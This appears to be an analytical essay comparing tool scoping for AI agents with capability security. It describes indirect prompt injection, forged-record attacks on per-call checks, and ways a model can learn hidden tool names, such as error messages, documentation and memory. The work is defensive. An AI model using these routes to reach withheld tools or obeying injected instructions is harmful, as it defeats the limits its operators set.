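# Hiding Tools from an AI Agent and Withholding the Reference: Does Tool Scoping Give Capability Security?

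## How an agent calls a tool, and where a tool can be taken away

An AI agent is a language model together with a *harness*, a program that lets the model act, for example by searching the web, reading files or sending email. Each such action is a *tool*, an ordinary named function. The harness builds the model's prompt, reads its output and runs the tools it calls. A harness can hold hundreds of tools, but most tasks need only a handful, so some designers protect an agent by showing it fewer of them. For example, an agent summarising a document would see a tool for reading files but none for running shell commands.

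Sidik and Rokach (2026) argue in *Beyond Static Sandboxing* that "an agent cannot misuse a tool it does not know exists". They built a *capability governor*, a component that chooses which tools an agent sees and may run in each session. Their reasoning resembles an older idea, *capability security*, which protects a resource by withholding any usable reference to it from a program and ensuring that the program can't forge or guess one. Whether the two approaches give the same protection depends on what happens between the model writing a tool's name and the tool running.

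### One tool call, step by step

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, uses a weather tool as the running example in its developer documentation. A call to the tool goes like this.

1. The harness describes the tool to the model. The description has a name, `get_weather`, a plain-English explanation, and a *schema*, which is a formal list of the arguments: a required text field `location` and an optional `unit` that must be either "celsius" or "fahrenheit". As Anthropic's *Define tools* explains, the company's interface turns these definitions into a system prompt, the text that comes before the conversation.
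2. The model writes a call. It produces text one small piece at a time, and the call is a stretch of that text in an agreed format, containing the name `get_weather` and the argument "San Francisco, CA".
3. A parser finds the call in the output and separates the name from the arguments. The prompt template that Anthropic publishes gives this job to regular expressions, a simple kind of pattern matching.
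4. The *dispatcher*, the part of the harness or tool server that looks up a tool by name, searches its table for `get_weather` and finds the function to run.
5. The function runs. It uses whatever credentials the developer gave it, such as a key for a weather service or the permissions of the operating-system account that started the harness. The result goes back to the model as more text, and the model either writes another call or answers the user.

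Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own". The model receives a tool's schema and the result of a call, but never the code that runs in between. That code holds the credentials, so the model can cause a payment without seeing the key that authorises it.

The dispatcher receives only a string from the model, with no record of why the model wrote it. The tool's name may have come from the list in the prompt. It may also have come from training. Anthropic publishes fixed schemas for a few common tools, such as `bash` for shell commands, and calls them "trained-in" because it optimised Claude on thousands of successful runs with exactly those signatures. Or the name may have come from a web page the model read a minute earlier, where an attacker had spelled out the name and arguments. Leaving a tool out of the prompt removes only the first of these sources.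 A designer controls only the list, and a tool's absence from it does not guarantee that the model doesn't know the tool exists.

### Four places to withhold a tool

A designer can take a tool away at four points along this path.

| Place | Term | What the designer does | What happens if the model writes the call anyway |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| The prompt | Prompt-level hiding | Leaves the tool out of what the model sees | The tool runs |
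| The dispatcher's table | Dispatch-level denial | Makes the dispatcher refuse the tool in this session | The dispatcher refuses, whatever the arguments |
| Each call | Per-call authorization | Adds a check, outside the model, of the tool and its argument values | The tool runs only if those values pass |
| The credential or reference | Withholding the reference | Gives the running code no key or reference to the resource | The code may start, but it has nothing to act with |

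Tools are often hidden from the prompt to save money and help the model choose well among them, rather than for security. Anthropic's `defer_loading` setting, for example, lets developers keep hundreds of tools out of the prompt until the model finds one through a search tool. The dispatcher must still run those tools, or the feature would be useless. *AgentWeave* (2026) presents a system that shortens the tool list before a model sees it, but explicitly warns that "routing should not be presented as a security boundary". For security, it calls for a deterministic check after the model has selected an action, which denies the call if anything goes wrong.

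Hiding tools greatly changes which ones models choose. In *Prompts Don't Protect*, Uppala (2026) built a registry of 507 tools and wrote 200 tasks that tempt an agent to use a tool outside its role. In one, an analytics agent gets a message from a supposed finance chief demanding an urgent refund. Three models (Qwen 2.5 7B, Llama 3.1 8B and Claude Haiku 4.5) picked a forbidden tool in 48.5 to 68.5 percent of tasks when they could see the forbidden tools and had no guidance. Listing the permitted tools by name and banning all others reduced this to between 4 and 37 percent. When a proxy removed the forbidden tools from the list shown to the models, the rate was zero.

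Uppala describes that zero as holding "by construction", so it follows from the design and is little evidence of what a model writes when an attacker gives it a hidden tool's name. The proxy also checks the agent's role again when a call arrives because, as Uppala points out, a compromised model may name a tool that the proxy never listed. The guarantee against hidden names comes from this second check, whereas the measured result is that written prohibitions fail.

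That second check is dispatch-level denial. In its simplest form, the dispatcher's table has no entry for the tool. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting models to tool servers, has separate requests for listing and calling tools, so a server that filters its list must also refuse calls to the tools it hides. Under the current specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a server returns the error "Unknown tool" when it receives a call for a name it doesn't have. Sidik and Rokach's governor shortens the list in the prompt and also writes a deny list for the runtime to enforce, so their design doesn't rely on their slogan alone.

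Denying a tool *for one session* takes more work than it used to. Older versions of MCP opened a session first, and every later request carried its identifier. The July 2026 revision removed these sessions, so a tool call is now a single self-contained request that any copy of the server can handle (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The specification also forbids a server from varying its tool list between connections, although the list may depend on the authorization sent with each request. Someone who wants a summarising session to have fewer tools than a coding session must now restrict the tools in the harness or give the two sessions different credentials.

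One restriction applies between the prompt and the dispatcher, while the model is writing a call. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes a mode that limits the text the model can produce at that point, so that a call can name only tools the harness has offered. This makes hiding considerably stronger for calls that come through that interface. But the dispatcher still accepts the same calls as before, so a second agent on a different model, or any other program that can reach the dispatcher, could still run the hidden tool.

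Neither hiding nor denial helps when the harmful action uses a tool that the task needs. In an example from *ToolFence* (2026), the user wants to pay someone, the agent properly has the payment tool, and an attacker's message tells it to pay into a different account. Removing the tool would stop the attack, but it would also stop the task. *ToolFence* instead records which source the account number must come from and checks the actual value before the call runs, which is per-call authorization. The same problem arises with private data, because the model may copy a confidential detail into a legitimate field of a legitimate tool. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) points out that a tool's availability and a valid schema determine only whether a call can be formed, not whether a particular piece of data may go to a particular destination.

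A per-call check is a security boundary only if it runs outside the model. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) describes a mechanism with two layers. In the first, the system prompt contains a signed, expiring token and an instruction that high-risk calls require it, which the model may ignore. In the second, code in the tool runtime refuses any high-risk call that lacks a valid token. When the researchers put a forged record into the context, GPT-4.1-mini attempted the forbidden call in 99.4 percent of runs, GPT-4.1-nano and GPT-5.1 in all of them, and Claude Haiku 4.5 in none. By construction, none of those attempts could execute without a valid token. Counting attempted calls can therefore give the opposite impression of the same system from counting executed calls.

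The remaining option is to withhold what the tool itself needs. If no code in the session holds a key to the mail server, no string that the model writes will send mail from it. However, many things that look like references are only names. An MCP server that keeps a shopping basket between calls gives the model a string such as `bsk_a1b2c3`, which the model repeats in later calls. For servers that know who is calling, the specification states that "a handle is a name, not a capability", and the server should check on every call whether the caller may use that basket. Where the server does not know who is calling, possession of the string is the only protection, so the specification recommends a long random string with a limited lifetime.

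### Authority, capabilities and deputies

The distinction between a name and a capability is much older than language models. When a Unix program wants to read a file, it calls `open()` and passes the file's name, with no proof that it may read the file. The operating system checks the account that the program runs under and either opens the file or refuses. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) uses this call to illustrate *ambient authority*, which it defines as authority "that is exercised, but not selected, by its user". All of the program's permissions apply every time it names something, even when somebody else supplied the name.

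A *capability* is an unforgeable reference that identifies a resource and gives the right to use it. The nearest everyday example is the file descriptor, the small number that `open()` returns. A process can't reach a new file by guessing a descriptor. It gets one by inheriting it or receiving it from another process, as UT Austin's lecture *The Confused Deputy* explains. Miller and colleagues consider descriptors almost capabilities, but not quite, because ordinary access lists control the channel that carries them between processes. In the full *object-capability model*, programs act only through references they created or received.

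A *confused deputy* is a program that another party steers into misusing the program's own authority. In the standard example, from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, a compiler overwrote a billing file because a user gave it that file's name. Agents recreate the conditions for this problem. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) observe in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* that the actor choosing an action, the user who requested the task, the runtime holding the credentials and the service receiving the request may all be different parties.

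An attacker usually steers an agent through *indirect prompt injection*, which means placing text in a document, web page or tool output that the model reads and follows as an instruction. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2023) introduced the attack and showed that such text can control whether and how a model calls other software. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, gives the example of a job applicant who hides in a CV an instruction to approve the application. He says models are vulnerable because they only predict the next token and have no built-in separation between instructions and data. He therefore calls them "inherently confusable" deputies and advises developers to use safeguards that contain no language model to limit what the system can do.

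The word "capability" has several meanings in this literature. Sidik and Rokach use it for a tool or skill, so their "capability governor" governs tools and does not issue unforgeable references. Surapani and colleagues also call tools "ordinary capabilities". On one page of the MCP specification, the `tools` "capability" that a server declares is a protocol feature, while in the warning about handles the word has its security meaning. The same confusion arose earlier in operating systems with "POSIX capabilities", a fixed set of flags that grant powers such as changing the owner of any file on the machine. Miller and colleagues show that these flags lack several properties of real capabilities. From here on, the word has only its security meaning, except in the name "capability governor", and never refers to how able a model is.

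These terms make the claim about unknown tools testable. Suppose an attacker controls some of the text that the model reads and can get the model to write a call with any tool name and any arguments. David C recommends planning for roughly this case, because he takes the worst outcome of an injection to be whatever would happen if the attacker had direct access to the tools. The test is to withhold a tool at each of the four places in turn, leave the other three open, and see what runs. This shows where withholding the tool limits what the attacker can cause.

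## What capability theory says a withheld reference guarantees

In Hardy's story of the confused deputy, the billing file was safe from the compiler until a user learned the file's name. Users not knowing a thing's name is therefore a different protection from users having no reference to it, though the two are easy to mix up.

### A compiler with two masters

The events took place at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, about eleven years before Hardy published his account in 1988. Tymshare kept the compiler in a directory called SYSX. A user started it by typing `RUN (SYSX)FORT` and could add the name of a file to receive debugging output. Tymshare had changed the compiler to collect statistics on which language features people used. The compiler wrote these to `(SYSX)STAT`, a file name written into its code. To allow this, Tymshare gave the compiler a "home files license",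 which let it write to files in its own directory.

The billing records were in the same directory, in `(SYSX)BILL`. A user "came to know the name", as Hardy puts it, and gave it to the compiler as the place for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system to open the file. The operating system allowed this because the compiler had its license, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

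Hardy finds a problem with each of the obvious repairs. The compiler could reject any file outside the user's own directory, but users have good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could reject anything in SYSX, but that directory didn't exist when the programmers wrote the code, and somebody with proper access to SYSX might want output there. It could reject the name `(SYSX)BILL`, but the directory held other sensitive files, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. The output code was correct when its programmers wrote it and became wrong when Tymshare later gave the compiler the license. Nobody could have noticed this without examining every place where the compiler wrote a file.

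According to Hardy, the compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the license, and no way to indicate which one it meant to use. Tymshare tried to fix this by adding a system call that let a program "switch hats". The compiler could then open the debugging file on the user's authority alone, and a request for the billing file would fail. But some applications soon needed more than two hats, and files weren't the only things that needed protecting. The rules for opening a file also kept growing, and they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s the last time Hardy wrote them down.

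The capability solution replaces file names with capabilities. The compiler starts with a capability to the statistics file, which it uses for writing statistics, and the user supplies a second capability for the debugging output. A user without a capability to the billing file can't direct the debugging output there, so the billing records stay unchanged even if the user knows the file's name and types it into the compiler's input.

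In *Gemini discusses Confused Deputy*, a mailing-list thread started by Miller (2026), the capability researcher Alan Karp wrote, "A confused deputy uses its permissions on a resource designated by someone else." He added that people often mistake the problem for a failure to check inputs or limit privileges. In his view, least privilege, the principle that a program should have only the permissions its job requires, has nothing to do with confused deputies. That seems slightly too strong, because a license covering only the statistics file would have protected the billing records. But the user could still have sent debugging output to the statistics file, which the compiler has to be able to write, so least privilege would have limited the damage without preventing the confusion.

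### Four models and seven properties

Many computer scientists believed that capabilities were just another way of writing down ordinary permissions. Miller and colleagues trace this belief to the *access matrix*, a table with a row for each *subject* (a user or program) and a column for each resource. Each cell lists what that subject may do with that resource. If you store the table by columns, each resource has a list of who may use it. If you store it by rows, each subject has a list of what it may use. The contents are the same, so the two systems look equivalent.

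Access control lists and capabilities aren't equivalent, because a table of current permissions leaves out how a program names a resource and how permissions change. Miller and colleagues compare four models to show the difference.

- **Access control lists as columns.** Each resource has a list of the subjects that may use it. Ordinary Unix and Windows file permissions work this way.
- **Capabilities as rows.** Each subject has a list of the resources it may use.
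- **Capabilities as keys.** A subject holds copyable keys, and to use a resource it chooses both a key and a door.
- **Object capabilities.** A permission is a reference to an object, and that object may hold references of its own.

Seven properties distinguish the models. "Unspecified" in the table means that the usual description of the model leaves the matter open.

| Property | Question | Columns | Rows | Keys | Objects |
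| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| A. No designation without authority | Does naming a resource always convey the right to use it? | No | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| B. Dynamic subject creation | Can subjects create new subjects? | Not in practice | Yes, in practice | Yes | Yes |
| C. Subject-aggregated authority management | Does the power to edit permissions go with the subject, rather than with the resource? | Not in practice | Yes, in practice | Yes | Yes |
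| D. No ambient authority | Must a subject select the authority it uses? | No | No | Yes | Yes |
| E. Composability of authorities | Can a resource also act as a subject? | Unspecified | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| F. Access-controlled delegation channels | Must X have access to Y before X can pass Y a permission? | Unspecified | Unspecified | No | Yes |
| G. Dynamic resource creation | Can new resources appear, each with its own permissions? | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |

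Least privilege needs properties B and G. B lets each run of a program have its own permissions instead of all of its user's permissions. G lets a permission cover one newly created file. The POSIX flags lack G, so none of them can cover a single file.

E makes it possible to withdraw access. Suppose one program wants to lend another access to a file and withdraw it later. It creates a forwarder, a small object that passes messages on to the file, and gives the borrower a reference to the forwarder. To end the loan, it tells the forwarder to stop passing messages on. The borrower still has its reference but can no longer use it to reach the file. This needs E because the forwarder is a resource to the borrower and a subject to the file. F matters for containing permissions, because under the keys model anyone with a key may copy it to anyone else.

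A and D are the two properties that bear on confused deputies, and A implies D. Every request has to indicate a resource. If indicating a resource always conveys the right to use it, the requester selects that right by making the request. No authority then applies without being selected, which is property D. D doesn't imply A, because in the keys model a subject must choose a key, which satisfies D, but can point at a door without having its key, which violates A.

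Miller and colleagues summarise the risk of confused deputies as "hopeless without D, best if A", and Hardy's compiler shows why. Without D, the compiler opens files by name with all its permissions applying at once, so even a perfectly careful programmer can't make it use only the user's permissions. With D, the compiler can hold one key for its own records and accept another from the user, and it stays safe as long as it uses each key for its proper purpose. But the user can still name one file while supplying the key to another, and the programmer has to handle the mismatch correctly. With A, the mismatch can't arise, because the user can designate the billing file only by handing over the right to write to it, and a user who has that right could write to the file without the compiler.

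### Why an unconnected object stays out of reach

Under property A, whoever has a reference can use it, so the only way to restrict use is to restrict who gets the reference. Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, split this into two requirements. A program must not be able to *generate* a reference it isn't entitled to, for example by guessing or computing it, and it must not *receive* one from another program.

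Unforgeable references meet the first requirement. File names can't, because, as Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) points out, anybody can make up any string of characters. For the second, the object-capability model limits the ways in which an object can come to have a reference. There are four:

1. *Initial conditions*: the object already had the reference when the system started.
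2. *Parenthood*: the object created the other object and received the first reference to it.
3. *Endowment*: the object's creator gave it some of the creator's own references at birth.
4. *Introduction*: another object, which had references to both, sent the reference in a message.

A system based on Hardy's case has four objects: a user's program, a compiler, an output file and a billing file. At the start, the user's program has references to the compiler and the output file. These are the only references in the system, so no object has a reference to the billing file. We consider three moves, writing x → y for "x has a reference to y".

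| Move | References it adds |
| --- | --- |
| The user's program sends the compiler its reference to the output file | compiler → output file |
| The compiler creates a helper and endows it with that reference | compiler → helper, helper → output file |
| The user's program sends the compiler the text "(SYSX)BILL" | None |

The compiler can now write to the output file. The third move accomplishes nothing, because no operation in this system turns text into a reference. The compiler can store the text, search it or send it to the helper, but it still can't reach the billing file.

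No sequence of moves, however long or clever, can create a reference between two groups of objects that start with none between them in either direction. Miller and Shapiro summarize this in *Paradigm Regained* as "only connectivity begets connectivity". An introduction adds b → c only if some object a already has a → b and a → c. All three must then be in the same group, so the new reference stays inside it. A newly created object gets references only from its creator, which has the only reference to it, so it belongs in its creator's group. The argument doesn't depend on what the objects' code does, so it covers malicious code as well as buggy code.

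The words "in either direction" are necessary. Suppose we add a billing program that has references to the billing file and to the compiler. The compiler has no reference to the program or the file, so it can't contact either one. But the billing program could send the compiler its reference to the billing file, which would let the compiler write to it. Whether this happens depends on the billing program's code. The graph alone can therefore show either that access is impossible or that it might be possible, and in the second case somebody has to read the code to rule it out.

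The billing program could also keep its reference and write to the file whenever the compiler requested it. Miller and Shapiro distinguish between permission and authority. *Permission* is what a program may do to the objects it has references to. *Authority* is every effect it can cause, including effects through other programs that cooperate. If the billing program writes to the file on request, the compiler has authority over the file without permission to access it. The distinction disappears for two groups with no references between them, because no message can pass between the groups and so nothing in one can act on behalf of the other.

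In Miller and Shapiro's model, plain data such as a number is "knowledge limited rather than permission limited". A program that can work out a number can have it, even if the number is somebody's private cryptographic key. But data provides only information, never access. A capability is a reference to something other than data, so a program cannot get one by working it out.

This allows people to run code they don't trust. In Miller and Shapiro's example, a customer wants to use a manufacturer's calculator program without letting it send financial data back to the manufacturer. The manufacturer supplies only code, which is data and contains no references. A *loader*, the part of the system that starts new programs, combines this code with the references the customer chooses. If the customer starts several calculators, they can't exchange messages with one another unless the customer connects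 them. The guarantee doesn't hold if the manufacturer instead supplies a calculator that is already running, because the customer can't see what references it has.

The proof depends on some operations being impossible. C++ doesn't meet this condition because a program can convert an integer into a pointer, which amounts to forging a reference. Java doesn't meet it because its mutable static variables are shared storage that lets objects interact without having references to each other. Miller and Shapiro also set aside *covert channels*, in which one program signals to another through a side effect such as how long an operation takes. A calculator with no references might still leak information that way, although this wouldn't give it a reference to anything.

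Unix gives programs references to files but also lets them open files by name. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes two file names to the program `cp`, which opens the files and copies one to the other. Since the user might name any file, `cp` needs access to everything the user can read and write. The command `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt` also copies the file, but the user's shell opens both files and gives `cat` two file descriptors. Those descriptors are all the authority `cat` needs. Yet `cat` also runs with all of the user's permissions, so withholding a descriptor doesn't protect a file the user can access, because a malicious version of `cat` could call `open()` on it by name. Miller and Shapiro conclude that object-capability systems differ from today's systems mostly in having eliminated access by name, since today's systems already have something close to capabilities. Hardy made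 a related complaint in 1988, that some systems that added capabilities to traditional mechanisms suffered more from the combined disadvantages than they gained.

### When a capability is a string

The discussion so far has treated references and text as different kinds of thing, and some systems enforce that difference. The kernel keeps capabilities separate from data in the capability operating systems KeyKOS and EROS, and the runtime does so in the programming language E. A program in such a *partitioned* system can instruct the kernel to use its third capability, but it never handles the capability's bits. Writing the number 3 into a message doesn't send the capability, because the recipient's third capability is a different one.

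A *password capability* is a string too long to guess, which the system accepts from anyone who presents it. The operating system Amoeba used password capabilities. *Comparing capability systems* (Karp, 2026) lists such opaque tokens as one of three types of capability system, alongside object references and certificates. A Google Docs link is a familiar example, and *Capabilities in production systems* (Shapiro, 2025) quotes Karp using it to illustrate capabilities.

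Copying is a much bigger threat to a well-made password capability than guessing. There are about 3.4 × 10³⁸ random 128-bit strings, so an attacker who tried a billion a second for a year would have roughly one chance in 10²² of finding a particular one. But anyone who reads the string in a log file can use it, so keeping it from a program means keeping it out of everything the program can read. The graph argument still applies, but every channel that carries text now counts as one that carries capabilities. This matters a lot for a language model because it reads and writes only text.

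An old dispute was about this difference. In 1984 W. E. Boebert argued that no unmodified capability machine could stop secrets from flowing from a higher security level to a lower one. His example has two levels. A low-level program may read and write a memory segment called Low, and may write to another called High but not read it. A high-level program may read and write High, and may read Low but not write to it. These rules should let information move up but never down.

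In Boebert's attack, the low-level program has a capability to write to Low and stores a copy of that capability there. The high-level program, which may read Low, reads the capability and can then use it to copy secrets from High into Low, where the low-level program can read them. Each step uses only permissions that the rules granted. Other researchers cited the result for years as proof that capability systems can't contain information.

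Miller and colleagues reply that the attack needs a system in which programs can send capabilities wherever they can send data. In a partitioned system, reading data and reading capabilities are separate operations with separate permissions. The two programs can be allowed to move data between levels in the permitted direction, but not to move capabilities between levels at all. The first step of the attack then fails or achieves nothing, because the high-level program can read only data from Low, even if the low-level program stores capabilities there for its own use. Such a system is still an unmodified capability machine by Boebert's definition. Miller and colleagues also cite a formal proof, from work on EROS, that any system with independent controls on the two kinds of transfer can enforce these rules.

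Miller and Shapiro give a second reply that needs no special memory segments. They put an object called a data diode between the two programs. One program can only write to the diode, and the other can only read from it. The diode accepts only integers, so a capability can't pass through. Because the diode connects the two programs, the graph alone shows only that a capability might pass, and ruling that out requires reading the diode's few lines of code. Boebert wrote in 2003 that his paper remained "no more than an offhand remark".

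His attack still works wherever the system can't tell a capability from data, as Miller and colleagues accept. They add that designers of some password systems have found ways around it. But plain password capabilities have no such defence. An integer-only diode wouldn't stop the attack either, since a string of bits is an integer and the high-level program could reassemble the password from it.

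### Deputies that already have the reference

The reachability argument protects a resource from programs that have no route to it. But a deputy needs its references to do its job, and capability theory gives considerably weaker guarantees that nobody else can decide how it uses them.

Miller and colleagues explain that a deputy loses the benefit of having separate keys if somebody points it at a locked door and it tries every key until one fits. Hardy's compiler would do this if it tried the user's key on the billing file and then, when that failed, its own. To stay safe, the deputy has to keep track of what each key is for. "No security model can prevent people from writing bad programs", Miller and colleagues concede, although a good one makes reliable programs easier to write.

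The same mistake is possible with object capabilities. Karp (2026), in *Confused deputy*, asked fellow researchers whether anyone had proved that capability systems can't contain confused deputies, and William Leslie answered that they can contain them. A deputy may put its capabilities in a map, a table from names to references, and let the client choose an entry. The client then supplies the name and the deputy supplies the authority, so the two are separated again, as they were at Tymshare. A dispatcher that looks up an agent's tools by name uses a table of this kind.

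Mark Miller replied in the same thread that the 2003 argument is narrow. The argument is, loosely, that a deputy is safe if it uses *only* object capabilities to designate things. He called this a severe restriction that many normal deputies don't satisfy, though he thinks most of them are safe anyway. His own rule of thumb, which is not a proof, is that a deputy is probably safe if it doesn't perform *rights amplification*, meaning operations that increase the authority a capability carries.

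Rajani and colleagues supply the proofs, and the results are mixed. They first needed a definition of a program that is free from confused-deputy attacks. Take any memory location that an attacker wants to change. The program is safe if at least one of two conditions holds for the value that ends up there:

- The attacker has no influence: the final value is the same whatever code the attacker runs.
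- The attacker needs no deputy: the attacker's own code could have written that value there directly.

They then modelled a compiler that reads its output destination from a location the attacker can write to. With ordinary access control, the attack succeeds. In their capability model it fails, because the attacker's code can't produce a reference to a file it isn't allowed to write, and so can't pass one on. This confirms the informal argument about property A for the case where the attacker supplies the reference.

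An attacker who lacks a reference can still affect what it points to through a deputy that has it. In the simplest example from Rajani and colleagues, a privileged program copies a number from a location the attacker can write to into one the attacker can't. If the attacker puts in 41 or 42, that number ends up in the protected location. The attacker never had or named a reference to that location, so nothing here violates the capability model. Rajani and colleagues compare this to SQL injection, where a web server with proper access to a database passes on a malicious input. In another example, the attacker controls only a true-or-false value, which determines whether the privileged program writes 41 or 42. An agent is in much the same position when an attacker steers it while it rightly has a reference.

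Rajani and colleagues do prove that capabilities stop all such attacks if neither the deputy's code nor its initial memory contains a reference to any protected location that interests the attacker. But a deputy generally needs such references to do its job, and they say that these restrictions make their language "useless for almost all practical purposes". Hardy's compiler would violate them because it needs a capability to the statistics file.

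Billing adds a difficulty because some influence on the bill is legitimate. In Rajani and colleagues' version of the compiler, the charge depends on the source file, so a user can change the bill by submitting a shorter program. This is how billing should work, but it counts as an attack under the definition above. Rajani and colleagues therefore let the programmer *endorse* a piece of code, which exempts it from the definition. Somebody then has to decide which influences are legitimate, because a graph of references doesn't show which ones are.

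Their alternative tracks where values come from. Each value carries a label showing the least trusted source that contributed to it, and the system checks the label before writing the value to a protected location. A number copied from the attacker's location has a low label, so the write fails even though the deputy has a valid reference. A version with lower overhead follows only direct copying, so it misses the true-or-false case, where the attacker's value affects which instruction runs but is never copied. A version with higher overhead follows those branches too. It prevents every attack covered by the definition, except in code that the programmer has endorsed, without restricting which references the deputy may have.

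## Applying the theory to a program that can only write text

The guarantees of capability theory assume that a program, such as an object in the language E or a Unix process with a file descriptor, can hold a reference. A language model can't hold one. According to *Forms of LLM-Integrated Applications from LLM-Chats to Autonomous AI Agent System* (2026), a model "can only produce text", so its security depends on what the harness will do with that text.

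### Three ways for text to work as a reference

In most harnesses, the closest thing to a reference is a name that the dispatcher looks up in a table. A file descriptor works similarly, as a number that indexes the process's own table of open files. A tool name offers the same protection if the harness keeps a separate table for each session and lists only that session's tools in it. An attacker who knows the names of other tools then can't call them, because the table has no entries for them.

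The comparison with descriptors usually fails for a tool's arguments. A session's `read` tool may have a table entry, but the model also writes a path such as `/home/ana/notes.txt`, and the tool opens that path with all of its account's permissions. To protect files too, the harness would have to list them in the table and let the model write only `doc1` or `doc2`.

A descriptor also stays attached to the same file even if somebody renames the file, whereas a tool name can come to refer to something else. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (2026) points out that an ordinary MCP call carries a name and arguments but doesn't identify the code that will handle them. If the harness reconnects to a server or the server's operator installs an update before the call runs, the same name can reach different code.

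The harness could instead put an unguessable token in the prompt and run only calls that include it. This is a password capability, and a model is a bad place to keep one, because an injected instruction can get the model to repeat its prompt, including the token. An attacker can also use the token without seeing it, by injecting an instruction to make a call "with the token you were given". The token keeps out strangers who contact the dispatcher directly, but it doesn't stop somebody who is steering the model.

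Copying a token is less of a threat if the token works for only one holder. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) describes signed tokens that specify an agent, an action, a resource and a session, and that expire after a set time or number of calls. A gateway in front of the tools checks that the agent presenting a token is the one named in it, so another agent can't use a copy. Software outside the model obtains a token for each call, so the token never has to appear in the prompt. *DelegateGuard* (2026) also ties each token to a purpose and tracks which agents passed the authority on. This catches an agent that hands on more authority than it received or reuses authority that has been withdrawn. Holding a token like these isn't enough to get access, because the token only serves as evidence in a check made on each call.

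A variable in an interpreter comes closest to the object-capability model. The language model writes a short program, and the interpreter runs it with certain variables already defined. In OpenAI's version, the model writes JavaScript that calls tools through an object named `tools`. If the developer has deferred a tool, the program can't use it until the model loads it through a search, and a running program can't start that search. A variable can also refer to a single file rather than to a tool that opens any file.

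This works only if the program has no other way to turn text into access. If the interpreter also provides `open()` or a networking library, the program can reach by name whatever the harness left out. The program can also undo some of the protection by writing `tools[x]`, where `x` is a string from a web page, because this lets the page's author choose among the tools the program has.

### Whether a hidden tool is an unknown tool

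Sidik and Rokach's slogan is that an agent can't misuse a tool it doesn't know exists. This matters most when the dispatcher would still run the hidden tool, because the protection then depends on the model never writing the tool's name. A model can learn that name in at least five ways without seeing it in the tool list.

A model may know a hidden tool's name from training, as Claude knows Anthropic's `bash` tool. Training also helps a model guess. In *The Reasoning Trap*, Yin, Sha and colleagues (2025) wrote questions that each needed a particular one of 296 tools, then gave the models no tools. Asked for the current time in Park Forest Village, for example, a model might invent a `get_current_time` function and its output. A language model judged how often the models did this kind of thing. The rate was 34.8 percent for Qwen2.5-7B, 74.3 percent for a 7B model distilled from the reasoning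 model DeepSeek-R1, and 5.1 percent for Qwen3-32B, or 8.8 percent with reasoning turned on. These are small models by current standards, and the experiment didn't test whether the invented names matched real tools. But tool names tend to follow conventions, so some guesses will be right.

Public documentation can reveal tool names that would be hard to guess. For example, an agent with web search can read the exact name `str_replace_based_edit_tool` in Anthropic's *Text editor tool*. Some agents are meant to learn tool names from documents. In the benchmark *τ-Knowledge* (2026), the knowledge base mentions internal tools that aren't in the agent's regular list. The agent has to find a tool's exact name, pass it to an unlocking function to learn the parameters, and then call the tool. An attacker who could edit a document in such a knowledge base could give the agent a name in the same way.

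Error messages can also reveal tool names. When a model calls an unavailable tool, the AI SDK library raises an error that lists the available tools' names (*AI_NoSuchToolError*). If a harness built its error messages from its full tool table and returned them to the model, one wrong guess would reveal the name of every hidden tool.

Earlier turns are another source of tool names. If a conversation started with more tools, its history contains the old calls, with their names and arguments. Saved notes can also carry names between sessions. Sidik and Rokach let their summarising session search the agent's memory, where a note from an earlier coding session might mention the shell tool.

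Finally, the attacker can write the tool's name in the injected text. Sidik and Rokach built their governor for OpenClaw, an open-source agent program that by default gives every session the same fixed set of tools. Anybody can look up the names of these tools, so a single malicious page could work against many installations.

Anthropic's documentation allows for the possibility that a model will name a tool it wasn't shown. Developers can disable individual tools in Anthropic's browser and desktop sets, which removes them from what Claude receives. The *Tool reference* tells developers to return an error if Claude "still names" a disabled tool. Strict mode, which would prevent the model from writing such a name, isn't available for these sets or for the connector that brings in tools from MCP servers.

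Noyan's *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* makes a similar claim about keys and passwords: "A credential that does not exist in an agent's context cannot be misused". This is true if "context" means everything the session's code can reach, but not if it means the prompt, because tools use credentials that normally never appear there. The slogan about tools needs the same correction. An agent can't misuse a tool if nothing in its session can turn the tool's name into a running function.

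### Scoring the designs

The table below scores four designs on the four properties from Miller and colleagues that matter most here. The scores and reasons are our own analysis, not a published result. We treat each agent session as a subject, and we treat the things that tools act on, such as files, accounts and web addresses, as resources. "True references" means that the arguments are references too and that the session cannot open things by name.

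| Property | Prompt-level hiding | Dispatch-level denial | Per-call authorization | True references |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| A. No designation without authority | No. Any text can name the hidden tool, and the tool runs. | For tools only. A denied tool's name is useless, but arguments are still ordinary names. | No. The model can name anything, and a separate rule decides. | Yes. Text that matches no reference designates nothing. |
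| D. No ambient authority | No. The tool's credentials apply to every call. | No. The credentials of an allowed tool apply to every call. | No. The check accepts a call if any permission covers it. | Yes. Using a reference selects the authority. |
| F. Access-controlled delegation channels | No. Telling another agent the tool's name is enough. | Not applicable. Sessions can't pass permissions on, because only the harness edits the lists. | Depends on the design. AgentCap allows only parent-to-child delegation within a session. | Yes, if references travel separately from text. No for plain tokens. |
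| G. Dynamic resource creation | No. The smallest unit is a whole tool. | No. The smallest unit is a whole tool. | Yes. A rule can cover one new file or account. | Yes. Each new resource can have its own reference. |

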